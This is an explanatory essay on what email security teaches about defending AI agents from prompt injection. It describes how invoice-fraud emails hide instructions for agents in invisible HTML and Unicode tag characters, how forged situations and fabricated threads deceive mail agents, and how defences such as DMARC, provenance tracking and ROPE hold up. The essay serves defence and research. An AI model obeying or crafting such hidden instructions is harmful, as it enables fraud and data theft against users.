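# What email security teaches about defending AI agents from untrusted text

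## How a message reaches a person, and how it reaches an agent

Email security is the set of checks a company puts between its staff and mail from strangers. Much of it exists because of phishing, in which a message deceives a person into giving up a secret or taking a harmful action. Companies have begun to connect the same mailboxes to AI agents, which are language models that read material and use tools to take actions such as sending mail, fetching web pages or making payments. These agents read mail from strangers, some of whom now write messages aimed at the agents.

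Some of what people have learned from decades of securing email is useful for defending agents, but a good part of email security works by helping a person judge a message. Once the text has fooled the reader, that help comes too late, and only limits on what the reader can do are left. The question for each defence adapted for agents is therefore whether it still holds after the text has deceived the model.

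### An invoice on its way to a person

A fraudster might pose as a company's regular supplier and email it a PDF invoice, with a note saying that the supplier has changed banks and giving the new account number. In this kind of fraud, called business email compromise, an email impersonates an executive or a supplier to obtain a payment, often with no link or attachment. According to Dynamic Business' *The new phishing trick aimed at the AI reading your inbox*, Australia's national cyber security centre ranks it with phishing among the most common threats to small businesses, because they often approve payments and account changes without checking independently.

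This kind of fraud can also be attempted on a large scale. Microsoft (2026) described a campaign of over a million emails in which a fraudster posed as the chief executives of many companies and asked their accounts departments to send nearly $50,000 by bank transfer. To support the story, the fraudster included a forwarded conversation between the chief executive and a software supplier, and a fabricated invoice.

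When the supplier's email arrives, the company's mail server usually authenticates the sender first, using SPF, DKIM and DMARC to check that the email comes from the domain it claims. These checks can expose a forged address, but they can't stop a fraudster who has broken into the supplier's real mailbox, because emails sent from there do come from the supplier's domain.

Next, a filter scores the message on features such as the sender's reputation and the wording, then delivers it, sends it to junk or blocks it. Many companies also pay for detonation, which means opening an attachment or link on an isolated machine to see what it does before delivering the message. The PDF in this example only displays an account number, so detonation detects nothing. URL rewriting replaces any links in the email so that each click first goes through a checking service, which can block a page that turned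 malicious after the email arrived.

The email then lands in the inbox, perhaps under a banner, a notice warning about the sender or content ("This message came from outside your organisation"). The reader, in this case an accounts clerk, must decide whether to trust it. The clerk might remember that the supplier said nothing about a new bank when they spoke last week, but might also have forty other invoices to get through. A suspicious clerk can press a report button to send the message to the security team, who can then find and remove copies in other people's mailboxes.

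This chain is poor at stopping invoice fraud because much of it looks for malicious code and malicious web pages, and the supplier's email contains neither. Stopping the fraud depends mostly on the clerk and on whatever checks the company makes before it pays.

### The same invoice on its way to an agent

In a second version of the example, the clerk has an accounts assistant, an agent that can read mail, fetch web pages, send mail and pay invoices. The supplier's email is the same except for an added passage addressed to AI assistants, which claims that the company has already verified the new bank details and that the invoice is due today. The clerk may never see this passage.

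The mail server authenticates and filters a message, detonates its attachments in a sandbox and rewrites its links before delivery, whether the recipient is the clerk or an agent. The two paths differ only after the message reaches the inbox.

1. The clerk types a request, say, to deal with this morning's invoices.
2. Ordinary software puts together the context, which is all the text the model has before it when it decides what to do next. At this point the context holds the developer's standing instructions, a description of each tool and the clerk's request.
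3. The model produces a tool call, a request that ordinary software carry out an action. Here the request is to fetch the unread mail.
4. The software fetches the mail and adds it to the context, the fraudster's email included.
5. The model runs again on the longer context and produces another tool call. It might look up the supplier's records, or it might pay. The cycle repeats until the model writes a reply to the clerk instead.

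Researchers at the security blog Insinuator (2025) reported that they extracted a real mail assistant's developer instructions, and the name and parameters of every function the model could call, just by questioning it through its chat window. The model also received background data, including the date and time, the user's account, stored memories about the user and some information about any email thread the user had open.

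The problem begins at step 4, after which a single context holds words from the developer, the clerk and the fraudster. The fraudster's words are untrusted text, meaning anything in the context written by someone whose instructions the agent should not follow. The software can label them as untrusted, but the model may still treat a sentence in the email as a command.

The agent's copy of the email can also differ from the clerk's. An email carries headers, metadata and often two versions of its body, one in plain text and one in HTML, the formatting language of web pages. In TechRepublic's *Scammers Are Targeting AI Agents*, Daniel Rapp of the email security company Proofpoint describes recent attacks in which the two versions were completely different. A mail program usually shows the clerk the HTML version, but an agent's software might use the plain text.

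Even within one version of an email, there are many places to hide a sentence. Arntz (2026), in *Phishing emails are baiting your AI assistant*, lists HTML comments, text made invisible by styling, encoded content and zero-width characters. Arntz notes that whether any of this reaches the model depends on how the tool extracts the email. For example, a tool that discards HTML comments is immune to an instruction hidden in one, but another tool may not be.

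Attachments and calendar entries can carry instructions too. Proofpoint examined tools that generate both. One example was a PDF that opened as an ordinary non-disclosure agreement but also contained an instruction to send out files, written in white text on a white page. VirusTotal, a service that runs a file past many antivirus products, reported no detections, because the only malicious content was text.

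The attack can begin without the clerk opening anything. In the scenario from Help Net Security's *How attackers poison AI tools and defenses*, the hostile email sits in the inbox until the assistant retrieves it during another task. Even if the clerk had correctly dismissed the email as rubbish that morning and left it there, the assistant would still retrieve it when asked to summarise the inbox in the afternoon.

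### Prompt injection

Prompt injection is untrusted text that makes a model do something its user did not ask for. OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* classes it as social engineering, in which a third party misleads the model, and likens it to phishing, which deceives people. Sublime Security's *Shut down prompt injection attacks targeting AI email agents and tools* instead compares it to SQL injection, an old attack on badly built programs in which someone types database commands into a website form and the database runs them.

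The programmer Simon Willison coined the term "prompt injection" in September 2022, after Riley Goodside had shown that a user could override a developer's instructions by typing a sentence into an application built on the language model GPT-3. In those early cases the attacker was usually the person at the keyboard, which limited the damage. In 2023 Kai Greshake and colleagues showed that an attacker could instead place the instructions in content that an application retrieved, such as a web page, and that this worked against Microsoft's Bing Chat. The user is then the victim, and the attacker doesn't have to use the application at all. Email makes the attack even easier, because anyone who knows the address can send text to the agent.

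Researchers call the 2023 version indirect prompt injection. Sublime Security, which sells email security, calls an injection "direct" if the text tries to make a mail agent act, and "indirect" if it tries to make an AI-based filter pass a malicious email as harmless. Researchers would call both indirect, because both arrive by email.

### What the attacker may want

With the accounts assistant, an attacker has a choice of three prizes.

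Attackers may try to make an agent send them private data, which security people call exfiltration. Nylas' *Prevent prompt injection in email agents*, a guide for developers, gives the example of an email that orders the agent to forward the last 50 messages to an outside address, and warns that a naive agent will obey. An agent that can fetch web pages can also leak a secret without sending mail, by requesting a web address on the attacker's server with the secret included in the address.

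Another is a harmful action, which in the example is paying the invoice. The agent's freedom to do this depends partly on what the clerk asked for. OpenAI advises against broad requests such as "review my emails and take whatever action is needed", because they make it easier for hidden content to mislead the model.

The attacker may also settle for a false summary, without getting the assistant to move money or leak anything. The assistant tells the clerk that a supplier has changed banks, that the details are confirmed and that payment is urgent, and the clerk pays. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) describes a real invoice email of this type that the security company Barracuda found. A hidden block in the email instructed the summarising AI to add a fake priority action that changed a vendor's payment details.

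An attacker does not need hidden text to trick an AI summarizer. Ahmed (2026), in *Fake Email Thread Tricks AI Summarizer Without Hidden Text*, reported a case in which a made-up conversation was enough.

False summaries deserve more attention than they usually get, because taking tools away from an assistant does not prevent them. Even if a company stops the assistant from making payments and sending mail, a fraudster can still deceive the clerk through the assistant's summaries, which the clerk trusts more than the inbox. Apollo Raines, who develops an AI code review service, told Arntz that people have learned to distrust email but "haven't learned to distrust their AI assistant".

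### Injections in real mail, autumn 2026

The supplier's invoice is an invented example, but it is close to a real case. On 22 October 2026, Sublime Security observed an invoice fraud campaign that contained a hidden instruction for AI agents. Its report on the campaign is dated 26 October, and Trent (2026) relays the details in *Prompt Injection Goes After the Inbox*.

To a human reader, the emails were ordinary fraud. The senders impersonated a North American cybersecurity company and attached invoices for around $88,000. Most of the emails went to financial controllers, and the display name and text made them appear to come from a co-founder or chief executive of the controller's own company. A fabricated reply chain made the request look like part of an earlier conversation, and the emails offered a 10% discount that was about to expire.

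The attacker hid the order in two ways. It was in an HTML element with zero height and width, in white text one pixel high. It was also written in Unicode tag characters, an invisible set that mirrors the ordinary keyboard characters at a fixed distance in the code table. The letter A is U+0041, and its invisible counterpart is U+E0041. A mail program displays nothing for these characters, but software that processes the codes can recover the text. The order was to forward the email, with its PDF unchanged, to an address beginning "ap.confirm" at the target's own company.

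The order asks for little and mentions no payment or secrets, but as Trent points out, one forwarded message may be enough to put a fraudulent invoice into the accounts-payable queue or start an automated process there. Because the message would come from the financial controller's mailbox, it would pass sender authentication, and the accounts team would see an invoice from a colleague.

Sublime tried the message on several models. Some never surfaced the hidden text, some included it in their summaries, and some recognised the injection and recommended reporting the email. None did the forwarding that the attacker wanted, although a model that repeats the instruction in a summary has at least passed it on to the user. Because the results varied by model, a company cannot infer much about its own agent from somebody else's test.

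Barracuda had published a similar find on 7 October, and its sample shows how such a message gets past the earlier checks. According to Mascellino, the email looked like internal correspondence, with the same mailbox as sender and recipient. It came from a public-sector domain and had a trusted spam score, which helped it pass filters that rely on reputation. It carried a locked attachment that a person could open with the password in the message, but Barracuda calls such attachments a blind spot for traditional security controls. The email also contained hidden text meant to make the assistant present it as legitimate or urgent, in case the human had overlooked it.

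Barracuda was already reporting malicious prompts inside harmless-looking emails in its *Threat Spotlight* (2025), so the idea had been in circulation for more than a year. But most of the prompts defenders found in that time targeted AI security tools instead. In June, Scholten and Filar (2026) wrote in *Adversarial prompt injection payload for evading AI-based detection* that almost all the injections Sublime Security was seeing in the wild aimed to trick these tools into judging an email harmless. In one such email that Sublime analyzed, the attacker had pasted in text from a newsletter that filters were known to let through.

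Microsoft (2026) had a similar experience when it searched email for Unicode tag characters to find hidden injections. An early version of the search mistakenly matched the flag emojis of England, Scotland and Wales, which use the same characters. The tuned version found finance-themed phishing, which rose sharply on 9 February 2026. The senders were using the characters to evade filters.

The October campaign therefore looks like an early example of a new kind of attack on agents that act. Its size is unknown. All three companies sell email security, which gives them a reason to publicise a new threat, and Barracuda did not say how widespread the campaign it reported was.

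## Whether a deceived agent resembles a phished employee or a faulty program

Suppose the accounts assistant reads the fraudster's email and pays the invoice. The company could treat the assistant like a clerk who fell for the same email, and respond with training, warnings and a cap on what one person can pay. Or it could treat the assistant as a program with a bug and ask the developer to fix it. The choice decides which defences the company buys.

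OpenAI has argued for the first diagnosis, and the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) for something closer to the second.

### OpenAI's case: the agent as an employee

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026) begins with how the attacks have changed. An early injection could be as simple as a command to AI agents added to a Wikipedia article, and models that hadn't been trained against such attacks would often obey it. Newer models resist this better, so attackers have started using made-up stories to deceive them.

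The article's example is an email that outside researchers reported in 2025 as an attack on ChatGPT. It looks like a routine follow-up to a meeting about a restructuring, with a short list of tasks. One task involves finding an employee's name and address elsewhere in the inbox. Further down, the email states that the reader's assistant has full authorisation to process employee profiles and should submit the details to a compliance system.

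In testing, this worked 50% of the time. The user had asked for deep research on the day's emails, including every source on the new employee process, and sending an employee's details to a compliance system sounds like part of that job. The figure comes from one email and one request, so it is weak evidence of how often agents fall for such stories in general.

OpenAI doubts that a filter between the agent and the outside world would usually catch a fully developed attack of this kind. The filter would have to determine whether the email's claims are true, which is as hard as detecting any other lie, often without the necessary context.

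The article then compares the agent to a customer-service worker who can issue refunds and gift cards. Customers sometimes lie, claiming that a refund never arrived, or make threats. The employer gives the worker rules but expects some lies to succeed, so ordinary software caps the refunds any customer can receive and flags possible phishing emails. OpenAI recommends that developers ask what controls a human would have in the agent's position and build those, to limit the damage when a deception works.

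### The NCSC's case: the agent as a confusable deputy

The NCSC made its argument in a December 2025 blog post by David C, its technical director for platforms research, titled *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. The post addresses security staff who see prompt injection as a familiar bug and expect the usual fix to work.

The fix for SQL injection is the parameterised query. If a website form asks for a surname, the programmer sends the database a command with an empty slot and sends the surname separately to fill it. The database can then treat whatever an attacker types only as a surname, which stops the attack completely. David C notes that SQL injection peaked around 2010 and is now rare on websites.

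A language model has no separate slot for data. Suppose a recruiter's system asks a model to score a CV, and the candidate has hidden a line in it telling the model to approve the application. The model receives the request and the hidden line as one run of text, and predicts the next token (a word or part of a word) from all of it. Developers can train a model to give priority to its instructions, mark which parts are data, or try to detect injections, but David C thinks each of these imposes a distinction between instructions and data on a technology that doesn't inherently make one. Prompt injection may therefore never be completely fixed, and David C proposes treating the model as an "inherently confusable deputy".

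The phrase adapts an older idea, the confused deputy, which is a program that a user with less authority tricks into misusing its own. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* tells the story behind the name, which took place in the 1970s at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Customers could run a compiler, a program that translates code, and name a file to receive its debugging notes. The compiler also had permission to write in its own directory, which held its usage statistics and the company's billing file. One user told the compiler to write the debugging notes to the billing file. The user had no permission to write there but the compiler did, so the operating system allowed it, and the billing information was lost.

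According to Hardy, the compiler acted with authority from two sources and had no way to keep them apart. The remedy was for users to give it a "capability" instead of a bare file name. A capability is a token that both identifies a file and carries permission to write to it. A user with no right to the billing file would have no token for it.

The accounts assistant is in the same position as the compiler. It has the clerk's authority to make payments, but takes the account number from a stranger's email. The compiler, however, used separate pieces of code to write its statistics and its debugging notes, so a programmer could specify whose authority each piece should use. The assistant generates a tool call from its whole context, and the call doesn't record which sentence prompted it. David C therefore calls the model inherently confusable, and advises companies to choose another technology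 if they can't tolerate the remaining risk.

Experimental evidence supports this view. Developers label the text in a model's context as coming from the developer, the user or a tool. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested whether the model's internal activity reflects these labels. They wrapped identical passages of web text in different labels and trained a simple classifier to identify each passage's label from that activity. Then they tried the classifier on text whose label and style disagreed. It mostly followed the style, classifying text that sounded like a user as the user's even when it was labelled as tool output. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the attacks succeeded 2% of the time where this confusion was weakest and 70% where it was strongest.

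### An objection to the phishing comparison

In a post about the agent in its Atlas browser, OpenAI compared prompt injection to "scams and social engineering on the web". The Decoder's *OpenAI admits prompt injection may never be fully solved* called that comparison misleading because phishing exploits human weaknesses such as inattention and time pressure, while prompt injection exploits a technical flaw in how language models work. A company can train its staff to spot scams, but only the developer can fix the model. On this view, likening the flaw to gullibility shifts responsibility onto users, or suggests that it is acceptable for agents to fall for scams because people do.

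One of OpenAI's own examples, which The Decoder retells, helps the objection. A planted email told the agent to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive. The user later asked for an out-of-office reply, and the agent came across the email and resigned on the user's behalf. It is hard to imagine an assistant of flesh and blood making that mistake. (OpenAI says that after a security update the agent notices the attempt and asks the user what to do.)

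Bruce Schneier and Barath Raghavan also compare models with people in *Why AI Keeps Falling for Prompt Injection Attacks*, on Schneier on Security. A drive-through worker refuses a customer who orders a cheeseburger and then asks for the contents of the cash drawer. The worker knows what is normal in the job and who is asking, has procedures to follow, and can stop and ask the boss when something feels off. A model tends to make the decision itself instead of asking. People still fall for elaborate deceptions. One caller who posed as a police officer persuaded fast-food managers to strip-search employees.

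Schneier and Raghavan are less sure than The Decoder that the whole fault lies in the architecture. They regard overconfidence and eagerness to please as training choices, and the lack of a habit of pausing as an engineering deficiency. They write that nobody yet knows how much of the problem is inherent.

### Agreement on design

The Decoder's objection to the explanation is a good one, but it applies less to the design advice in OpenAI's later article, which gives most of the responsibility to the people who build the agent. The two camps largely agree on design. OpenAI wants software to limit what a deceived agent can do, just as it limits the refunds a worker can issue. David C wants designers to focus on deterministic safeguards, which are limits that ordinary code enforces whatever the model has concluded, such as keeping powerful tools away from a model that is reading strangers' mail.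 Neither expects much from filters for known bad phrases, since an attacker can always rephrase.

The NCSC repeated the point in interim advice on 20 August 2026, after several incidents in which AI models took unauthorised actions. *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that the NCSC told organisations not to rely solely on safeguards built into a model or agent framework.

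People still disagree about how well future models will resist deception. OpenAI expects a maximally intelligent model to resist social engineering better than a person, though it concedes that using one won't always be feasible or affordable. If OpenAI is right, a company might raise its assistant's payment limit as models improve. But the limit should depend on how much the company can afford to lose if models are inherently confusable.

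### A test on mailbox agents

*Your Mailbox Is Mine* (Wu, Nan and colleagues, 2025, revised 2026) tested both kinds of attack on agents that manage email. Some emails openly gave the agent orders. Others gave a believable but false account of the mailbox's condition, which made the harmful action look like a sensible next step.

In the controlled part of the study, the researchers built agents from six models and four software frameworks. They ran 480 trials of each attack, divided among four goals: stealing private mail, sending phishing to a contact, giving the user false information, and flooding or deleting messages. The four standard attacks that openly gave orders succeeded in 4.58% to 8.13% of trials. The attack that used a forged situation succeeded in 73.54%, ranging from 57.5% against Claude Sonnet 4.6 to 85% against DeepSeek-V3.2.

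An official-sounding tone does not explain the gap, since emails that another model wrote in the voice of a mail administrator, but without the carefully forged situation, succeeded only 22.5% of the time. Two reviewers read the models' visible reasoning in all 353 successful attacks. In every one, the reasoning treated the false situation as real and the attacker's action as something to finish before getting on with the user's task. Phished employees behave similarly, as when a clerk pays a fake invoice thinking that it is part of the job.

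The researchers then repeated the trials with defences in place.

| Defence | Forged-situation attacks that still succeeded |
|---|---|
| None | 73.54% |
| General instructions and labels marking email as untrusted | 71.25–72.92% |
| A model checking the text for attacks | 69.58–71.04% |
| An instruction to distrust unverified claims about the mailbox | 60.63% |
| A model checking whether the agent's actions fit its task | 37.50% |
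| Rules on which tools the agent may use for the task | 26.67% |
| Checking the claimed situation against the mail provider's records | 0% |

The last defence is a program that runs before the agent acts on a claim about the mailbox. It checks the claim against the mail provider's records over an authenticated connection, and blocks the action if they disagree. If the claim is true, the program still checks that the action and its recipient fit what the user asked for. Wu and colleagues designed it around this one attack, so the zero result is unsurprising and does not show that the program would stop other attacks. For example, it could not verify a claim that a supplier has changed banks, because a mail provider has no record of that.

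Separately, the researchers attacked 63 real email-agent applications, using test mailboxes and made-up secrets. They hijacked all of them, with each of the six models and on every compatible mail service they tried. They could retry each attack until it worked, which took fewer than two attempts on average, so the result isn't comparable with the 73.54%. They reported the weakness to 67 vendors, and 22 acknowledged it, but the vulnerabilities were still unfixed when the study came out.

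The results favour OpenAI's account of what a successful attack looks like. Models had mostly learned to refuse orders from strangers, but strangers' lies still deceived them. But the employee comparison would be a poor guide to the remedy if it led a company to rely on warnings. Warnings hardly helped, while ordinary code that looked up the facts stopped the attack.

### Agents fall for different things

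Resisting lies and resisting orders seem to be separate abilities. In *SEA*, He, Han and colleagues (2026) had an AI attacker pose as someone the user trusted and hold long conversations with agents that controlled simulated money and accounts. On the Chinese tasks, the attacker succeeded 16.9% of the time against GPT-6 and 84.3% against Qwen3-8B, a small open model. When the attacker also inserted explicit orders, its success rate rose to 42.5% against GPT-6 but fell from 35.0% to 15.6% against Claude Opus 4.6. The researchers think Opus recognised the orders as an attack and became more careful about everything else.

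In the mailbox study, undisguised orders worked poorly on their own. Here they made a persuasive conversation more effective against most of the models, so a company that tests its agent against one kind of attack can't assume it has covered the other.

Agents also fall for different lies than people do. In *AgentPhishing*, Tan, Li and Zhao (2026) first gave six email agents phishing messages from public collections, many from the 2000s. The agents caught every one. The researchers then had a model write new emails and improve its method based on how each agent responded. The adapted emails were much better at fooling four of the six agents. Qwen3.7-Plus's score rose from 0.12 with the first generated emails to 0.95 with the adapted ones, on a scale from 0 (safe) to 1 (worst possible). The scores for Claude Sonnet 5 and Gemini 3.5 Flash hardly changed.

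Requests that seemed to continue existing work were more dangerous than urgent ones, which agents tended to recognize as attacks. GPT-5.4 detected a quarter of the phishing emails when Tan and colleagues framed them as ongoing work, and all of them when the emails used authority and urgency instead. The batches were small, but the result suggests a problem with giving an agent the company's phishing training, which tells staff to watch for urgency.

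### How an agent differs from the clerk

Four differences affect whether an email defence will work for an agent.

1. Reading and acting happen in one process. The clerk reads an email in one program and pays in another, and may have second thoughts in between. An agent can read the email and request the payment in its next step. It could use that step to check the story instead, but agents seldom do. In He and colleagues' tests on Chinese tasks, the 11 models verified on average about 14.5% of the claims they could have checked, and the best managed 31.6%.

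2. A warning to a model is itself text that the model has to interpret. It goes into the same context as the email it warns about, and the email can contradict it. A clerk can also ignore a banner, of course. But the finding by Ye and colleagues that style can outweigh labels suggests that an attacker has more room to argue with a warning when the reader is a model.

3. Copies of a model share weaknesses. Two clerks at neighbouring desks have different memories and suspicions, and one may catch what the other missed. Two agents with the same model and the same software have the same blind spots, so an attacker can rehearse on one before writing to the other. Some weaknesses even carry over between models. Tan and colleagues wrote one set of instructions for generating phishing emails and tried it on nine agents that had played no part in developing it. Four of them detected fewer than 10%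 of the emails and complied with more than 45%.

4. A company can test a model thousands of times. It can send its staff only so many simulated phishing emails before they grow tired of them or learn to recognise the tests, but a model can start each trial with no memory of the last. He and colleagues ran more than 8,000 attacks. The company can also change one setting and run everything again. Attackers get the same benefit if they can obtain a copy of the agent.

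Copies of the same model can differ in how easily they are deceived, because developers give them different standing instructions. *The System Prompt Is the Attack Surface* (2026) reports that people fail roughly 9% to 20% of the time in controlled phishing simulations, and that email agents could fail more than 97% of the time under some instructions. The researchers had searched for instructions that would produce bad results, so these figures do not show that agents are five times as gullible as staff. But a model that tests well may do worse after a developer rewrites its instructions.

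### The question to ask of each defence

OpenAI and the NCSC both expect some attacks to succeed, so a company should check whether each defence still works after an attacker has deceived the model.

Once an email has deceived an AI assistant, a label saying that the email is untrusted no longer protects against it, because the label was meant to influence the model's judgement, which has already gone wrong. A rule in the payment software that allows the assistant to pay only into bank accounts already on file still works, because the software compares two account numbers and the email's story has no effect on the comparison. Some defences, such as a second model that reviews the first one's actions, fall in between. The second model may not be fooled by the first deception, but the attacker can try to deceive it as well.

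Defences that fail this test can still be useful. OpenAI reports that most of the attacks it knows of against ChatGPT fail because safety training makes the agent refuse, and each refusal leaves one fewer attack for the other safeguards to handle. But it would be a mistake to give an agent more power only because it refuses attacks.

The comparison also has to include the person who reads the agent's output. An agent that can't make payments can still write a false summary that leads a clerk to make one. The company then needs a check that works even when the email has deceived both the agent and the clerk.

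## Establishing who wrote the text

The first defence in email security is to check where a message came from. Mail servers compare addresses and verify signatures before delivery, so no claim in the text can change the result. The check therefore works even when the text would deceive its reader, but it establishes less than people often assume.

### What SPF, DKIM and DMARC check

An email has two sender addresses. The reader sees the From address. The sending server gives the receiving server the other one, the envelope address, where bounce notices go. A fraudster can put someone else's address in either.

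SPF (Sender Policy Framework) checks the envelope address. A domain's owner uses the DNS, the internet's public directory of domains, to publish a list of the servers that may send its mail. The receiving server looks up the envelope domain's list and checks whether the connecting server is on it.

Under DKIM (DomainKeys Identified Mail), the sending server signs the message with a private key and names the domain that takes responsibility for it. The receiving server checks the signature with the matching public key, which it fetches from that domain's DNS records. A valid signature shows that the sender had access to the private key and that nobody has altered the signed parts since.

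Neither SPF nor DKIM checks the From address. A fraudster can register a domain, list a server for it, sign with its key and pass both checks while showing the reader somebody else's address. DMARC closes this gap by requiring alignment, which means the domain in the From address must match a domain that either SPF or DKIM has verified. *Domain-Based Message Authentication, Reporting, and Conformance (DMARC)* (Herr and Levine, 2026), the current standard, defines a strict form, in which the two domains must be identical, and a relaxed form, in which they need only belong to the same organisation's domain. Nearly all domain owners find the relaxed form sufficient.

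Suppose the supplier in the running example owns the domain brightpaper.example, and a fraudster who owns cheaphost.example forges the supplier's address.

| | Supplier's real invoice | Forged invoice |
|---|---|---|
| Domain in the From address | brightpaper.example | brightpaper.example |
| Domain in the envelope address | mail.brightpaper.example | cheaphost.example |
| SPF | Pass | Pass |
| Domain in the DKIM signature | brightpaper.example | cheaphost.example |
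| DKIM | Pass | Pass |
| Alignment with the From address | Yes | No |
| DMARC | Pass | Fail |

The forgery passes SPF and DKIM because the fraudster controls cheaphost.example, but it fails DMARC because that domain is unrelated to the one the clerk would see.

### What happens when a message fails

A domain's DMARC record includes a policy for mail that fails. The domain owner can choose "none" to express no preference, "quarantine" to ask receivers to treat the message as suspicious, or "reject" to ask them to refuse it. The receiver makes the final decision. Herr and Levine forbid receivers to reject a message solely because the policy is "reject". Without other evidence, such as the domain's usual sending patterns, receivers must treat the message as if the policy were "quarantine".

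This caution exists because legitimate mail can fail these checks too. If a university relays a graduate's mail to a private mailbox, the mail arrives from the university's server, which is not on the original sender's SPF list. The DKIM signature usually survives relaying, but a mailing list that adds a footer can break it. If a company rejects such mail, the list's software may treat its employees' addresses as dead and unsubscribe them.

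Herr and Levine admit that few receivers follow the advice, and they doubt that receivers ever will. Mailing lists have adapted by rewriting the From address. ARC, a protocol for preserving authentication results when a server forwards mail, is not widely used.

What happens to the forged invoice therefore depends on the supplier's policy and the mail provider of the clerk's company. If the supplier chose "none", DMARC gives the provider no reason to divert the message. If the supplier never published a DMARC record, DMARC doesn't apply.

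### Adoption and the bulk-sender rules

Many domain owners don't set up email authentication unless they have to. *Lazy Gatekeepers* (2025), a study of SPF, cites earlier scans of the million most popular websites, which found SPF records on 45% to 54% of them. Governments have had more success by making it compulsory. *The Coverage Gap* (2026) puts DMARC adoption at about 12% of Chilean government domains, where it is voluntary, and at more than 95% in the comparison countries that required it.

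The large mail providers have since imposed their own requirements. Kumaran (2023), in *New Gmail protections for a safer, less spammy inbox*, announced rules for anyone sending more than 5,000 messages a day to Gmail addresses, and Yahoo announced similar requirements. Since February 2024 these bulk senders have had to use both SPF and DKIM, publish a DMARC record and align the From address with SPF or DKIM. According to its *Email sender guidelines FAQ*, Google began stricter enforcement in November 2025, with temporary and permanent rejections. Microsoft's *Policies, Practices, and Guidelines* says similar rules for Outlook.com, with the same threshold, began on 5 May 2025.

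Google's own figures, reported in Valimail's *Google stats show why DMARC and email authentication matter*, suggest a large effect. Gmail users received 65% fewer unauthenticated messages, a drop of 265 billion in 2024. Valimail, which sells DMARC services, also counted 2.5 million domains that added authentication or DMARC records in the first sixty days of that year.

Many of the missing unauthenticated messages presumably came from legitimate businesses that set up their records and kept sending, so these figures don't measure how much fraud was prevented. Valimail adds that most email marketers chose the policy "none", which satisfies Google but does little to stop others from forging their addresses.

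The rules also do little to stop the forged invoice. Google applies them only to mail for personal Gmail accounts, not to the Workspace accounts that companies use, and a fraudster who writes to a few dozen accounts departments sends far fewer than 5,000 messages a day. Google's *Email sender guidelines* require only SPF or DKIM from smaller senders to Gmail, and the fraudster can set up either one for their own domain.

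### What a pass does not prove

A DMARC pass shows that the domain's owner authorised the use of the domain. Herr and Levine stress that it does not verify the part of the address before the @ sign or show that the message is safe. A fraudster can therefore pass DMARC in several ways.

The simplest way around DMARC is to register a lookalike domain such as brightpaper-billing.example and authenticate it properly. Another is to write from any domain and set the display name to "Bright Paper Accounts". Herr and Levine place both methods outside DMARC's scope.

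A fraudster who has broken into the supplier's mailbox or gained control of a subdomain's DNS records also passes. Relaxed alignment lets someone who controls old.brightpaper.example send mail as brightpaper.example, which strict alignment prevents.

The sender may also be honest. A colleague who receives the fraudulent invoice might forward it to the clerk and ask whether it looks right. The forwarded message comes from the company's own domain and passes every check, even though it contains the fraudster's words below the colleague's. The October campaign tried to get an agent to do the forwarding so that its text would pass the checks in the same way.

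An agent that relies too much on domains can become worse at detecting phishing. In *The System Prompt Is the Attack Surface*, Litvak tuned instructions that told agents to compare the domain of an email's sender with the domain of its links. With the best version, agents caught 93.7% of phishing emails and wrongly blocked 3.8% of legitimate ones. When an attacker registered one domain and used it for both the sender and the link, the detection rate with the tuned instructions fell by up to half. In 98% of the missed emails for which Litvak analysed the model's reasoning, the model had treated matching domains as a sign of legitimacy. Some models that were already good at spotting phishing became worse when told to look for this one clue.

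Litvak's test did not use DMARC results, but an authenticated lookalike domain would exploit the same behavior. The model follows its instructions and checks a fact that the attacker controls.

### Passing the origin on to an agent

The receiving mail server can record its authentication results in a header for the agent's software to read. The software must accept only the header its own server added, since a sender can forge one. It can then show the result to the model or use ordinary code to act on it, for example by withholding mail that failed. Only the second option still works if the email deceives the model.

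Most other material an agent reads comes with no comparable check on who wrote it. An encrypted connection identifies the website that served a page but not the person who wrote a comment on it. A shared document reaches the agent as one run of text, even if ten people edited it. In a forwarded thread, the earlier messages are text inside the latest one, and the person forwarding it can edit or invent them. The invoice fraudsters took advantage of this by fabricating reply chains.

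The software that runs the agent can at least record where it fetched each piece of text. In provenance tracking, it labels the text with that origin on arrival and keeps the label as the text moves through the system. It stores the labels outside the model's context, where neither the model nor an attacker's text can change them. The software can use the labels to warn the model, or to withdraw tools once text from a stranger arrives.

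Keeping the labels is difficult because a tool call doesn't record which text prompted it. A system called CaMeL deals with this by turning the user's request into a program and recording the source of each value as the program runs. A newer system, ROPE, lets the model work freely and checks the values in each action just before the action runs.

### How ROPE works

*ROPE* (Ma, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) separates the question of who wrote a text from whether that author may give orders, two questions that email security tends to treat as one. The paper's example is a digitally signed advertisement. Its author is certain, but the user never asked for it, so nothing in it should determine what the agent does.

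ROPE trusts three sources: the user's request and account identity, content from an authenticated sender whom the request names, and the user's own records, such as a log of past payments.

1. Before anyone uses the agent, its developers list every tool that changes something or sends data out. For each tool they mark the sensitive parameters, such as the recipient of a payment, and set a default rule for where each value may come from.
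2. When the user makes a request, a language model called the router reads it and adjusts the rules to suit the task. The router never sees the emails or web pages the agent goes on to read, so an injection in them can't influence it.
3. As the agent works, ordinary code labels each piece of incoming text using the platform's records, such as an email's verified sender. It ignores what the text claims about itself. A web page or file counts as one untrusted block, even if the user named it, unless something like a signature ties all of it to an author.
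4. When the agent tries to use one of the listed tools, ordinary code looks for each protected value in the sources its rule accepts. If the value isn't there in full, the code blocks the call.

No language model takes part in the last step, so the check still works for protected values even if the attacker has completely deceived the agent. But it doesn't test whether the agent chose sensibly among permitted values, so an injection might still make the agent pay the wrong one of two known suppliers.

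### Results and costs

Ma and colleagues tested ROPE with four models on AgentDyn, a benchmark of 60 coding, shopping and everyday tasks, using 560 attack cases for each model. Attacks succeeded 0.2% to 0.3% of the time with ROPE, compared with 49.6% against GPT-4o-mini without a defence.

The protection reduces the number of tasks an agent completes. With no attack under way, GPT-4o-mini finished 46.7% of the tasks without a defence, 36.7% with ROPE, and 18.3% with DRIFT, which checks the agent's actions against a plan made from the user's request. Across the four models tested, ROPE kept at most 84% of a model's undefended performance. All four models are old, and newer ones would probably finish more tasks, with or without ROPE.

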